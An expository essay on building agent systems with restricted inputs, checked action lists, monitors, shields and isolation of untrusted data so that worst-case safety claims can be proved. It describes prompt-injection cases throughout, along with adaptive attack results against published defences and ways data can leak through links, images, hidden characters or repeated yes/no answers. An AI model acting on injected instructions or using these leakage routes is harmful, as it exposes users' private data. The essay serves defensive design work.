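# Restricted interfaces and constrained action spaces as routes to worst-case guarantees for AI systems

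## Worst-case claims and why open-ended models resist them

A language model is a program that takes a piece of text and produces another, one token (a word or part of a word) at a time. Companies now connect these models to mailboxes, calendars, databases and payment systems, where a bad output can delete a record or move money. Nobody can yet prove that such a model will behave well on every text it may receive. Restricted interfaces and constrained action spaces are ways of building the surrounding software so that certain bad events cannot happen even when the model behaves badly. Security engineers have used the same idea since the 1970s, putting programs they do not trust behind small mechanisms that check each access.

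An open-ended model accepts free text or images and may return any text or request any action. An agent is a language model in a loop that calls software tools and reads their results. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes the loop. On each turn, the surrounding application sends the model the conversation so far and a description of the available tools. The model returns either an answer to the user or a tool call, which is a request to run an outside function, such as sending an email, with arguments the model chooses. The application runs the function, adds the result to the conversation and queries the model again, until the model returns an answer. The model only produces tokens, so a call runs only if the application executes it. A monitor is ordinary software that allows or denies each action the model proposes, and its policy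 is the set of rules it applies.

Suppose an assistant can read emails, create calendar events and send emails. Its user asks it to read the three newest emails and create a calendar event if one of them asks for a meeting. Two of the emails come from colleagues. The third comes from a stranger and includes an instruction to forward the latest message in the mailbox to an outside address. All three are untrusted data, meaning content that someone other than the user or the developer may have written. If the model follows the stranger's instruction, the stranger has carried out a prompt injection. The main event to rule out is private mail leaving the mailbox. A less serious one is the creation of a calendar entry for a meeting that nobody wanted.

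### Two kinds of claim

Developers can make two quite different promises about such an assistant. An average-case claim states that something bad is rare over a stated distribution of inputs. Write f(x) for what the assistant does on input x, B for the set of bad outcomes and D for the distribution from which the inputs come. The claim is then

P(f(x) ∈ B) ≤ ε, for x drawn from D

where ε is some small number. A worst-case claim states that something bad never happens for any input or attacker in a stated class X:

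for every x in X, f(x) ∉ B

Since models choose their tokens partly at random, x has to cover the random draws as well as the text.

The Alignment Research Center's *Estimating Tail Risk in Neural Networks* deals with the first kind of claim. Its example is a hypothetical engineering assistant M with a detector C for catastrophic suggestions, and the goal is to estimate the probability that C flags M's output M(x). In *Adversarial training for high-stakes reliability*, Ziegler, Nix and colleagues (2022) base the choice between the two kinds of claim on the stakes. Good average performance is enough when no single action can be catastrophic, but worst-case performance is what matters when one could be.

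The average-case claim, unlike the worst-case claim, does not cover inputs that somebody chooses on purpose. Suppose one incoming email in ten million has wording that makes the assistant forward mail. Over ordinary correspondence, the average-case claim holds with an ε small enough to satisfy most users. But a stranger who finds that wording and sends it is not drawing from D, and the attack may work every time. The average-case claim also offers less assurance when a model is used very often. *Estimating Tail Risks in Language Model Output Distributions* (2026) points out that people query these models billions of times a day, and at that rate a failure with a chance of one in a billion happens daily.

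Testing supports only the average-case claim. Nazeri, Schmuck and colleagues (2026), in *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models*, show what it can establish for a single fixed prompt. If none of n sampled outputs is harmful, a standard confidence interval gives, at the 99% level, an upper bound of 1 − 0.005^(1/n) on the probability of harm. That is about 0.5% after a thousand samples and about five in a million after a million. The bound never reaches zero, and it holds only for that prompt. Their method searches the tree of possible outputs for harmful branches and adds up the probabilities of those it finds. The sum is a lower bound that holds with certainty, so it can prove a model unsafe on a prompt but cannot prove it safe. *Safety Is Π₁, Provability Is Σ₁* (2026) explains this asymmetry in logical terms, since a single finite run can refute a safety claim but no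 list of passed tests, however long, covers every input.

### Too many inputs, and no short cut through them

The simplest way to establish a worst-case claim is to test every input. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, there are 100,000^1,000 = 10^5000 possible prompts of 1,000 tokens, a length that three emails can easily reach. A machine testing 10^18 prompts a second for ten billion years would cover about 3 × 10^35 of them. The number of possible outputs grows with length in the same way.

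A proof need not check cases one by one. A few lines of school algebra can settle a question about infinitely many numbers, and engineers verify some control software by similar reasoning. Nazeri and colleagues doubt that existing techniques carry over to language models, because these models have an enormous number of input and output dimensions and generate text randomly. *BEAVER* (2025), however, reports sound verification of the output distributions of five open-weight models with 4 to 70 billion parameters, for privacy leaks, insecure code and toxic text. An output distribution is the set of probabilities a model assigns to its possible replies to a given prompt, so verifying it for one prompt does not show that the same property holds for all prompts.

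Computability theory also limits what a guard, a program that inspects each output before anyone uses it, can guarantee. *No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard* (Amer, Kinczel and Long, 2026) proves that, for a model able to produce any finite string, a guard can block everything a policy forbids and nothing it allows exactly when the policy is decidable. A policy is decidable if some algorithm always halts with the right verdict. If a guard erred on only finitely many strings, adding a table of corrections would produce such an algorithm. For an undecidable policy, every guard therefore errs on infinitely many strings, and a guard that lets nothing forbidden through must block infinitely many permitted outputs. Policies that judge code by what it does when it runs can be undecidable.

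*Pandora's Toolbox Or Why Agent Safety Cannot Be Verified* (Franco and Gershenson, 2026) reaches a similar result for agents that can run programs. It constructs an agent that runs a harmless program p and, if p ever stops, runs a dangerous program q. The agent is unsafe exactly when p stops. An algorithm that could always predict whether such agents are safe would therefore solve the halting problem, which no algorithm can do.

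These theorems assume unlimited string lengths or running times, which real systems don't have. When Franco and Gershenson impose finite bounds, the question becomes decidable. It is still hard, because it is PSPACE-complete, and the time taken by known solutions to such problems grows exponentially with the size of the problem. Amer and colleagues stress that a system can make infinitely many errors and still have a low error rate in ordinary use. Even if no method can settle every case, a designer can still build a particular system whose case is easy to settle.

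### No definition of harm to prove things about

Even if the computing problem were solved, a worst-case claim would still need a set B that a proof can refer to. For a robot, B might be the positions in which it touches an obstacle. Nobody has a comparable set for free text. Nazeri and colleagues acknowledge that they cannot write out the set of harmful responses, so they use an oracle instead, which may be a list of banned words, a trained classifier or a human moderator. Their proofs are therefore about the oracle's verdicts, and apply to harm only to the extent that the oracle is right. The Alignment Research Center similarly assumes a catastrophe detector, and acknowledges that it does not know how to build one with the required properties.

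Part of the difficulty is that people disagree about what counts as dangerous. Franco and Gershenson give the example of a program that harms Bob but not Alice, which Alice may consider safe. They leave the definition of danger open and assume only that someone can supply one example of a dangerous program. Amer and colleagues conclude that a rule of the form "never output X", where X depends on meaning or effect, is better written as a tolerated error rate under a stated pattern of use and a stated adversary. This is sensible advice, but following it means giving up the worst-case claim for such rules. In the email example, a program can check that no message goes to an outside address, but it can't check that no message misleads its recipient.

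### Attackers who adapt

Experiments have done the most to discourage worst-case claims about models. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked twelve published defences with methods tuned to each one. Some of the defences target prompt injection and others target jailbreaks, in which the user tries to extract forbidden content. The defences fall into four families: added instructions in the prompt, extra training on known attacks, separate filter models that classify inputs or outputs, and checks that rely on a secret the attacker is assumed not to know. The original papers had mostly reported attack success near zero.

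All the attacks repeatedly propose texts, score them, and revise the best ones. In the search version, a second language model revises the texts, for up to 800 queries per scenario. Another version trains the attacking model by reinforcement learning, and a third uses gradients from the target. The researchers also ran a competition with $20,000 in prizes, in which more than 500 people tried to write injections by hand. Most of the prompt-injection tests used AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated workplace and travel tasks with tools.

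The attack success rate was above 90% for most of the twelve defences. For MetaSecAlign, a model trained specifically to resist prompt injections, it rose from a reported 2% to 96%, and the reinforcement-learning attack succeeded every time against two other training-based defences. The table shows Nasr and colleagues' AgentDojo results for defences added around a general model. The fixed attack is a template included in the benchmark.

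| Defence | Fixed attack, Gemini-2.5 Pro | Adaptive search, Gemini-2.5 Pro | Adaptive search, GPT-5 Mini |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30% | 100% | 75% |
| Spotlighting (delimiters around trusted text) | 28% | 99% | 47% |
| Prompt Sandwiching (user's request repeated after the data) | 21% | 95% | 69% |
| Protect AI (filter) | 15% | 90% | 81% |
| PIGuard (filter) | 0% | 71% | 49% |
| PromptGuard (filter) | 26% | 94% | 75% |
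| Model Armor (filter) | 28% | 90% | 56% |
| MELON (second run with a hidden dummy task) | 0% | 89% | 71% |

The fixed attack never succeeded against GPT-5 Mini, even with no defence in place, while the adaptive search succeeded in 75% of cases. A zero success rate on a fixed test set is therefore weak evidence that a model will resist an attacker who can revise the attack. On the 29 scenarios that both the human competitors and the search attempted, the search broke 69%, while the competitors collectively broke all of them.

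The attackers had generous access, including in some cases the filter's own confidence score. The tests also differed between defences, so the rates can't be used to rank them, and breaking these twelve defences doesn't prove that every other defence will fail. Training has also made injection harder. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026), in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, cite Anthropic's figures for its model Claude Opus 4.5 in coding tasks, where attacks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. If every attempt had an independent 4.7% chance of success, the rate would have reached 99% by the hundredth attempt. Some of the scenarios therefore evidently resist repeated attack, but a 63% success rate is still far from a guarantee that attacks will never succeed.

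Narisetty and colleagues also give a reason to expect the problem to last. Databases were once vulnerable to a similar attack, in which user input was treated as part of a command, and engineers stopped it by setting the structure of the command before inserting the input. That worked because database commands have a grammar that separates code from data. Natural language has no such grammar, and developers train models to follow instructions wherever they occur in the text.

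### Moving the claim from the model to the system

Nasr and colleagues left one group of defences out of their search experiments: those in which the model fixes its plan before anything untrusted arrives. In most of the chosen scenarios the attack would have failed by construction. They add that such designs suit a limited set of tasks and are no panacea, but the omission points to a different kind of claim. Let y be whatever the model returns, and let S(x, y) be what the whole system then does. The new claim is

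for every x in X and every possible output y, S(x, y) ∉ B

Since y ranges over everything a model could return, including what it returns after following the stranger's email, the proof needs facts only about the ordinary software that turns y into an action, not about the model's weights or training. Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, think general-purpose agents are unlikely to give reliable guarantees while they rely on the current class of models, but that a system may stay secure even if its model is vulnerable. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) applies the same idea to agents that act by writing code. A compiler rejects any program that exceeds its access rights, regardless of who or what wrote it.

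In the email example, a monitor that denies every call to the sending tool stops the forwarding, whatever the stranger writes or the model returns. This holds only if the calendar tool cannot send invitations to outsiders, since an invitation could carry the mail out. The monitor does not stop the model from adding a bogus meeting to the calendar.

The undecidability results do not rule out this approach when the policy names actions. Amer and colleagues prove that a monitor that sees every action and can stop any of them exactly enforces any policy that names a set of harmful actions. A program can recognise a call to the sending tool just by comparing names. But if one permitted action is running arbitrary code, and the policy concerns what that code does, the difficulty that Franco and Gershenson describe applies in full. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) therefore makes enforcement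 guarantees depend on a formal policy, usually over a well-defined set of actions. Users and regulators say what they want in ordinary language, and existing systems typically use a model to translate this into a formal policy, though nobody has validated the model's translations.

Designers can restrict the system at three points. They can accept only structured inputs, such as a form with a few fields, so that X is small enough to check. They can allow only actions that someone has checked beforehand, so that every y leads to an acceptable action or none. Or they can keep untrusted data away from the part that decides what to do, so that the stranger's email can supply a meeting date but cannot change which tool runs.

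## The case for small input spaces and checked actions

An engineer can test a program on all of its inputs if there are a few million of them, but not if there are 10^5000 possible prompts. Supporters of restriction base their case on this difference, and they apply it to actions as well as inputs.

*From Transformers to Weighted Automata* (2026) points out that a tester who cannot look inside the model has to query every input in the worst case. The paper concludes that practical verification needs input sets with a compact description, such as a formal grammar or a logical constraint, so that a proof can cover many inputs at once.

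### Inputs that someone can check in full

Suppose the developers of the email assistant replace free text with a form for booking meetings. The user picks a date in the next year (365 values), a start time on the half-hour (48), one of four lengths and one of 200 colleagues. That gives 365 × 48 × 4 × 200 = 14,016,000 possible requests. At 1,000 requests a second, a tester can try them all in under four hours. If the software always returns the same output for the same request, these tests support a worst-case claim about the form without any theory of how the model works. Adding a free-text title would make exhaustive testing infeasible, because a 50-character title using only 26 letters and the space has 27^50, or about 4 × 10^71, possible values, and each can be combined with any of the 14 million requests.

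Listing the inputs is also impossible when they are measurements such as distances and speeds, which can take any value in a range. But a range with only a few dimensions has a compact description, and a solver can analyze all of it at once. The best-known example is ACAS Xu, a collision-avoidance system for unmanned aircraft. According to *Reluplex* (Katz, Barrett and colleagues, 2017), the system's developers first stored its advice in a lookup table of more than 2 GB, which raised concerns about memory on certified aircraft hardware. The developers then explored replacing the table with 45 small neural networks that together take up less than 3 MB. Each network has five inputs: the distance to the other aircraft, two angles and the two speeds. It scores five possible pieces of advice (clear of conflict, or a weak or strong turn to the left or right), and the system gives the one with the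 lowest score.

Earlier certification work had relied on 1.5 million simulated encounters, which cannot rule out a bad input between the simulated ones. Katz and colleagues instead looked for a proof. Each network has 300 ReLU units, each of which outputs its input if positive and zero otherwise. Once a solver fixes which units are on and which are off, the network is a linear function, and standard methods can settle any linear question about it. But 300 units have 2^300 combinations, about 2 × 10^90. The Reluplex algorithm avoids checking most of them. It searches for an input that breaks the property, letting its trial values temporarily violate the ReLU rule and then repairing them. It splits the problem into an "on" case and an "off" case only after five repairs to the same unit. Splitting about a tenth of the units often settled all the others.

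The team tested ten properties. Two require that a network never report "clear of conflict" when the other aircraft is directly ahead, and both held on all 42 networks tested. A property about distant, slower aircraft held on 41 networks after about 110 hours of computing, and the solver ran out of time on the other four. One property remained undecided. Another failed because the solver found an input on which the network disagreed with the original table, and there had already been hints of this fault in simulations. A further property failed on 35 networks, but the behaviour was acceptable, so the mistake was in the property.

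These results are the model for the whole approach, but they have limits. Katz and colleagues proved statements about the advice and left for future work a proof that aircraft following it avoid each other. Their solver used rounded arithmetic, so they do not claim complete soundness. They also proved that the general problem is NP-complete, so no known method avoids exponential time in the worst case.

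### What verifiers handled in 2025 and 2026

Current tools mostly push a range of inputs through the network, layer by layer, and compute bounds on the output. Vorobyov and Ilyushin (2026), in *Scaling Neural Network Verification with Tensor Parallelism and Fully Sharded Data Parallelism*, give a small example. Let x₁ and x₂ each lie between −1 and 1, and let a layer compute y₁ = x₁ + x₂ and y₂ = x₁ − x₂. Both results lie between −2 and 2. If the next layer adds them, a method that uses only these intervals gives a range of −4 to 4 for the sum. But the sum is 2x₁, which lies between −2 and 2. The wider bound is sound, because it leaves out no possible value, but it may be too loose to prove a true property. Better methods track how each quantity depends on the original inputs. A complete verifier, one that always reaches an answer given enough time, also splits the problem into smaller parts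 whenever its bounds are too loose.

The annual competition VNN-COMP shows how far this goes. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, 2026) lists the networks in the latest round, and the table gives some of them.

| Benchmark | Task | Parameters | Input dimensions |
|---|---|---|---|
| safeNLP | Classifying sentences | 4,000 | 30 |
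| ACAS Xu | Turn advice for aircraft | 13,000 | 5 |
| ViT | Classifying images with a transformer | 68,000 to 76,000 | 3,072 |
| CIFAR-100 | Classifying images | 2.5 to 3.8 million | 3,072 |
| cGAN | Generating images of a road | 500,000 to 68 million | 5 |
| VGGNet16 | Classifying images | 138 million | about 150,000 |

The largest network in the 2026 competition was no bigger than the largest in 2025, the year covered by *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)* (Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues, 2025). The best tool in 2026 settled 3,164 of the 3,373 problems in the main track, producing 1,982 proofs and 1,182 counterexamples. The competition now allows 116 seconds for each ACAS Xu problem, whereas the original runs took anywhere from seconds to days.

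The largest networks are checked only over tiny input regions, so their parameter counts make verification look more general than it is. For VGGNet16, a typical question is whether small changes to the pixels of one particular image can change its label, and some problems vary only a single pixel. Another benchmark moves a camera by about a hundredth of a millimetre. Networks that have to satisfy a property over their whole operating range, such as safety certificates for simple control systems, have only 1,000 to 4,000 parameters and two to six inputs. The headline score also overstates the tools' ability, since a deliberately minimal verifier entered as a baseline settled 1,551 of the problems. The best tool still struggles on harder problems. Ladner and colleagues report that it ran out of time on 2,994 of 60,000 checks of image classifiers, with 1,000 seconds allowed for each check, even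 though the developers had trained those classifiers to be easy to verify. One of the classifiers labels 83.5% of test images correctly, but the tool could prove for only 66.0% that the label was both correct and stable under small changes.

Transformers, the networks behind language models, are even harder to verify. For the ViT benchmark, the organisers of the problem set cut the models down to two or three layers and replaced one standard component with an easier one. *Certified Mechanistic Interpretability* (2026) verifies synthetic transformers of up to 265,000 parameters, at about 54 seconds per sample, and reports some experiments on the 124-million-parameter version of GPT-2, a language model from 2019. Memory is one obstacle. Vorobyov and Ilyushin calculate that one layer with 4,096 inputs and 262,144 units needs about 4 GB for its weights alone, before the verifier stores any bounds.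 They halved peak memory by splitting the work across two graphics processors, but this made the bounds far looser in deeper networks. A second method kept the bounds identical and saved 34 to 39% of memory on wide networks. These savings are too small to make verifying a model with tens of billions of parameters feasible.

The safeNLP benchmark comes closest to verifying something about free text. One of its two tasks is to recognise when a user asks whether they are talking to a robot. A separate language model turns each sentence into a list of numbers, and a small network classifies the list. The proposers generate rewordings of a sentence, draw the smallest box around the resulting lists, and use the verifier to try to prove that the small network classifies every point in the box correctly. Such a proof does not cover the language model that produced the numbers, and a new rewording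 may land outside the box.

Verifiers can also be wrong. In 2026 the winning tool gave one answer that the organisers counted as incorrect or lacking a valid counterexample, and another leading tool gave 94 such answers. In 2025 Kaulen and colleagues found that the same input could produce different outputs on different hardware because of rounding, so four hours of testing the booking form on one machine may not show what it will output on another.

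### Typed fields and trained conventions

A typed field gives some protection even when nobody can verify the model behind it. If a field accepts only a date, the program that reads the form rejects everything else, so a stranger's instruction to forward mail never reaches the model. This guarantee comes from a few lines of ordinary code, though the stranger can still enter a wrong date.

Some defences use a similar structure inside the prompt. StruQ, which Chen, Piet and colleagues proposed in 2024, separates the developer's instruction from the outside data with reserved markers. A filter removes any copy of the markers from the data, so an attacker cannot forge the boundary. The developers then train the model on examples where the data contains planted instructions and the correct answer ignores them.

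The filter is ordinary code, and anyone can check that no marker gets past it. But the model still processes all of the data, and only its training makes it less likely to follow instructions there. Attackers therefore look for wording on which the training fails. Narisetty and colleagues cite work in which an adaptive search over token strings raised the success rate of attacks on StruQ from near zero in the original results to about 100% on one benchmark and 80 to 100% on another. They also cite measurements by Zverev and colleagues, who found that neither prompting nor further training reliably makes current models separate instructions from data.

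A structured prompt is still an open-ended input. Its layout may lower the rate of successful attacks over ordinary inputs, which supports an average-case claim. A worst-case claim requires enforcing the restriction before the model reads the input, for example with a parser that rejects malformed dates.

### Choosing from a list of actions

Many applications need free-text input because their users want to describe problems in their own words. For these applications, supporters of restriction limit the system's actions instead of its inputs. In the simplest version, which Beurer-Kellner and colleagues call the action-selector pattern, the model reads a request and picks one or more actions from a list that the developers wrote beforehand. The results of the actions never go back to the model.

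One example is a customer-service chatbot that can take only three actions: fetch a link to the customer's last order, direct the customer to the settings page for passwords, or direct them to the settings page for payment details. A malicious request can make the model choose the wrong action, but cannot add a fourth. The developers need to check only that each action is acceptable whenever this customer might trigger it. An action that issues a refund would fail that check unless ordinary code first confirmed that the customer was owed one.

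Because the results never return to the model, instructions hidden in an order record or an email cannot influence it. This restriction also rules out many tasks. In the email example, an action-selector could open the three newest emails for the user, but it could not create a calendar event based on their contents. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues apply the pattern to two of the ten applications they work through. They also allow templates, which are actions with blanks for the model to fill in. An action is still easy to check if the blank is for an order number, but a blank for the text of a message brings back the open-ended output that the list was meant to remove.

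Constrained decoding can force the model to stay on the list. A language model assigns a probability to every possible next token. Constrained decoding sets the probability of each token that would break the required format to zero, rescales the rest and then samples as usual:

P′(t | text so far) = P(t | text so far) ÷ (total probability of the allowed tokens), for each allowed token t

If the software works correctly, every output that isn't cut off early fits the format. A parser that rejects malformed outputs gives the same guarantee, though the model may need several attempts.

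The guarantee covers only the form of the output. If the format requires a meeting date and no email mentions a meeting, the decoder will still produce a well-formed date, because the format has no value for "no meeting". The developers can add one, but the model may choose it wrongly too.

Forcing a model's output into a fixed format can even make the answer worse. Suppose the format permits only "Yes." and "No.". Without the constraint, the model would begin with "Yes" 90% of the time, but it would almost always continue with ", but only if" and would put a full stop straight after "Yes" in just 1% of those cases. It would begin with "No" the other 10% of the time and put a full stop straight after it in 90% of those cases. The model would therefore write "Yes." with probability 0.009 and "No." with probability 0.09, so a plain "No." is ten times as likely. Under constrained decoding it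 answers "Yes." 90% of the time, because the decoder accepts the first word and then blocks the condition that would usually follow.

### From single actions to sequences

An agent usually takes several steps, and allowing only actions that are harmless on their own does not guarantee that a sequence of them is harmless. An agent might have 20 allowed actions, including "read file" and "send email". Reading a private file harms nobody while its contents stay inside the system, and an email with nothing private in it is harmless too. But an agent that can do both can leak the file by reading it and then emailing its contents.

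With 20 possible actions, there are 20^10 sequences of ten steps, or about 1.02 × 10^13. A checker that examined a million a second would need about four months, and each additional step would multiply that time by 20. About 880 billion of the sequences, or 8.6%, contain a "read file" later followed by a "send email". Nobody can approve that many sequences one by one, and the count doesn't include the actions' arguments, such as which file and which address.

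The developers can instead prove an invariant, a statement that is true at the start and that every permitted action keeps true. The monitor can store one bit that records whether the agent has read a private file, and refuse every email once the bit is set. The invariant is "no email has left since the agent first read a private file". To prove it, the developers check each of the 20 actions in both states of the bit, for a total of 40 cases. By induction, the invariant then holds for action sequences of any length. The proof assumes that "send email" is the only way data can leave and that the monitor sets the bit whenever any action reads private data, including actions whose names don't suggest it, such as "search".

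This rule is crude because it also blocks emails unrelated to the file, which may make the agent useless after its first read. More precise rules track individual pieces of data, which takes more bookkeeping but relies on the same kind of argument.

Small outputs add up in the same way. A yes/no answer carries at most one bit of information, which seems too little to leak anything important. But suppose an outsider may put yes/no questions to an assistant about a mailbox that contains a six-digit password-reset code. The outsider asks whether the code is below 500,000 and then keeps halving the remaining range. Since 2^20 is slightly more than a million, 20 truthful answers reveal the code. In general, k answers from a menu of m options carry at most

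k × log₂ m bits

A single choice among 20 actions can carry 4.3 bits, and a visible sequence of ten such choices can carry 43 bits. The same calculation applies to isolated agents that return only short answers from a fixed set.

To guarantee a worst-case limit on leakage, the monitor therefore has to count all the answers so far, across conversations and accounts. With a limit of ten answers, the outsider in the example still faces about 1,000 possible codes. But the count doesn't measure how much each bit matters. If the secret is whether a company will accept a takeover offer, the first answer reveals it.

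### Shields and backup controllers

Refusing an email always leaves the agent in a safe position, so the monitor only has to check one step ahead. Physical systems can enter states in which nothing has gone wrong yet but no action can prevent an accident, so a rule that forbids only the accident itself can take effect too late. Suppose a car drives on a track divided into cells. At each step it can change its speed by at most one, and it then moves forward as many cells as its new speed. If it is at speed 4 with five free cells ahead, then even under the hardest braking it moves three cells, then two, and hits the wall on the next move.

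Researchers in reinforcement learning, in which a program learns by trial and reward, deal with this by means of a shield. Alshiekh, Bloem and colleagues set out the method in *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding* (2018). The designer writes a simplified model of the environment with a finite number of states and marks the unsafe ones. An algorithm then finds the states from which safety can be kept for ever:

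1. Start with every state that is not marked unsafe, and call this set W.
2. Remove from W each state in which every action might lead outside W, given all the ways the environment could respond.
3. Repeat the second step until nothing more drops out.

The process stops because there are finitely many states and each round removes at least one. In every state that remains, at least one action always leads back into W. The shield permits only such actions, so a system that starts in W never reaches an unsafe state, whatever the learning program proposes. The shield can give the program a list of permitted actions before it chooses, or replace a forbidden choice afterwards.

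For the car, the remaining states are those with at least v(v − 1)/2 free cells ahead at speed v, because full braking covers (v − 1) + (v − 2) + … + 1 cells. At speed 3 with nine free cells, the shield blocks acceleration because the car would then be at speed 4 with five free cells, and it needs six to stop. The shield allows the car to hold its speed because that leaves six cells, and stopping from speed 3 takes only three.

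A shield can support a worst-case guarantee even when the learning program is large and opaque. But the designer has to list the states, and their number multiplies with each new variable. Ten variables with ten values each give ten billion states. The guarantee also depends on the environment responding only in the ways the designer listed. If a car brakes less on an icy track than the model assumes, the shield may permit a fatal move.

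Run-time assurance needs less computation. Engineers pair the complex controller with a simple backup controller whose behaviour they can verify, and a switch hands control to the backup before the system reaches a state the backup can't recover from. Lui Sha described this arrangement, known as the Simplex architecture, in *Using Simplicity to Control Complexity* (2001). The proof needs facts about the backup, the switch and the physical system, but none about the complex controller. In the car example, the backup might brake as hard as possible, so engineers only need to work out which states braking can recover from, rather than search through every possible strategy. If the backup can recover from only a few states, the switch has to act early, and the system may then spend much of its time under the less capable controller.

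An office agent often has an easy fallback, which is to stop and ask the user. This works for the forwarded email because a delay does little harm, but it doesn't work for an agent halfway through moving a database, where stopping may leave the records in a worse state than finishing or never starting.

### Actions that arrive with a proof

A list or a shield covers only the cases its designers worked out in advance. Some supporters want to allow new actions as well, provided each one comes with a proof that it is safe. Finding a proof can be very hard but checking one is routine, so a powerful, untrusted model can search for the proof and a small program can check each step. If the proof is wrong, the checker rejects it and the action does not run.

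*Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple, Skalse et al., 2024) gives the best-known version of the proposal. In it, a world model describes mathematically how the system's actions affect the world, a safety specification states which effects are acceptable, and a verifier produces an auditable proof that the system meets the specification according to the world model. The verifier can also prove a bound on a probability, for example that the chance of an overloaded power line stays below one in a million under the world model. This bound holds for whatever the AI system proposes, so it is stronger than a test result, but it still depends on the probabilities in the world model.

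For the email assistant, the world model would be a short list of which tools can send data outside and which files are private, and the one-bit invariant could serve as the specification. For a power grid, engineers already have good equations. An assistant that gives people advice would need a model of how readers react to sentences, and nobody knows how to write one. The proposal is therefore most convincing where engineers could have written a specification without any AI.

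In 2024 the UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA), a public funder of high-risk research, started its Safeguarded AI programme to develop this idea. The programme had a budget of £59 million, with Dalrymple as its director. At launch, the plan was to build languages and tools for writing world models and checking proofs, train AI systems to use them, and demonstrate the result in areas such as energy networks. This plan does not show that the method works at that scale.

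Melo, Máximo and colleagues make a more general claim in *Machines that halt resolve the undecidability of artificial intelligence alignment* (2025). They accept that no algorithm can decide whether an arbitrary AI system meets a non-trivial standard of alignment. But they argue that developers can start with a finite set of operations proved to be aligned and combine them into infinitely many larger systems that are aligned by construction. They add that every such system should be guaranteed to halt, meaning that it reaches a final state after finitely many steps.

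The first part of the argument is right, and compilers that accept only programs of a certain form already work on this principle. But the construction works only if combining aligned operations always gives an aligned result. This can fail when a designer judges each operation separately, as "read file" and "send email" show. The construction succeeds when every operation preserves the proved property, as with the one-bit invariant. The hard part is finding such a property and proving that each operation preserves it, which the general theorem doesn't do.

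The halting condition achieves less than the title suggests. It excludes the agent that Franco and Gershenson constructed, whose safety depended on whether another program ever stops. But language models with a limit on output length already halt, as do agents with a limit on the number of steps, and nobody can prove in general that they are safe. A question about all inputs can also be undecidable even if the program halts on each one. For example, a program could take an even number greater than two, check whether it is the sum of two primes, and forward the mailbox if it is not. This program always halts, but proving that it never forwards the mailbox would require proving Goldbach's conjecture, which dates from 1742 and which no number of test runs can prove. Bounding the inputs as well as the steps would make the question decidable, and the computation needed to check it would then depend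 on how small or well structured the developers had made the input space.

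## The case for isolating untrusted data

An email assistant has to read whatever people send, so its developers cannot restrict its input to a form with fixed fields. Limiting it to a menu of actions doesn't help much either when the next action has to depend on a message's contents. Other designs accept free text but limit what it can influence. Their designers assume that an attacker can fool any model that reads the attacker's text, and they build the surrounding software so that fooling the model has little effect.

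In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) compares the danger to a confused deputy, the computer security term for a program tricked into misusing its rights by someone who has fewer. An email assistant can read, send and delete its user's mail. If the model treats a stranger's message as an instruction, the stranger can get the assistant to do these things too. In a later commentary on Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, Willison advised designers to assume that anyone who can slip text into a model's input controls everything the model produces next, including its tool calls. This assumption is pessimistic, since many attacks fail, but designers who adopt it don't have to predict which wordings will work.

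Supporters of isolation consider filters and user approval weaker defenses. Willison (2025) argues in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that if a filter catches 99% of attacks, an attacker can look for the other 1%. Asking users to approve every action works only while they keep reading the requests, and Willison expects most people to start clicking "OK" as fast as they can.

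Under Willison's rules, a model that reads untrusted text may not call any tool that an attacker could abuse. If it also sees private data, it may not produce links or images, because either can carry the data to an attacker's server in its web address, and an image does so as soon as the assistant displays it. A single model under these rules makes a poor assistant, so the designs below divide the work and apply the rules only to the parts that read untrusted text.

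An attacker can change which actions such a system takes or corrupt the data those actions use. Suppose a user asks an agent to pay an invoice. Text in the invoice might make the agent email the user's files to someone. If the invoice contains no hidden instruction but gives the attacker's account number, the agent takes the actions the user wanted but pays the wrong person. A system has control-flow integrity if untrusted data cannot change which actions are possible, their order or their conditions. It has data-flow security if untrusted data cannot corrupt the arguments of those actions or the values that decide between branches. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) matches each property to a mechanism that protects it: dividing the work between two models for control flow, and labelling the data for data flow.

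### Committing to a plan

In the plan-then-execute pattern, the model lists its tool calls before it reads anything untrusted, and the software then refuses any call not in the plan. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an assistant to send today's schedule to their boss, John Doe. The assistant plans to read today's calendar and then send an email to John Doe's address. If an outsider wrote one of the calendar entries, that entry cannot add a third step or change the recipient. It can still change the body of the email, because the model writes the body after reading the calendar.

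The strength of this protection depends on what the planned tools can do with arguments the attacker chooses. For a file-sorting assistant, the plan might allow only the commands for finding and moving files, but a malicious file could still make the model find sensitive documents and move them to a public network drive. Replying to email carries a similar risk. If the user asks the assistant to answer a message with information from recent mail, the plan has to include a search and a reply. If the sender is the attacker, a hidden instruction in the message could make the model search for something more sensitive and encode it in the reply in invisible characters, without departing from the plan or changing the recipient the user chose.

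A plan can include repeated steps and conditions. To tell regular collaborators about a holiday, an assistant must send an unknown number of emails to people it has yet to identify, so its plan must be able to repeat a step. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think an email assistant's choice of actions should rarely depend on untrusted data. Costa and colleagues call a task data-independent if one fixed sequence of tool calls solves it whatever the data contains. Forwarding the three newest emails to a named colleague is data-independent, but creating a calendar event only if one of those emails contains a meeting request is not, because the plan needs at least one condition.

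### Reading each document separately

If one model reads several documents together, a malicious document can affect how the model treats the others. The map-reduce pattern prevents this by giving each document to a separate model call that has no tools and may return only a restricted answer. A second stage then combines the answers.

Suppose a user wants this month's invoices sent to the accounts department. In the first stage, a separate model call for each file answers yes or no to whether it contains an invoice. The second stage sends the files marked yes. An attacker can get a malicious file included in the email, but could have done that anyway by writing a fake invoice. The file cannot make the agent open other files or change the address.

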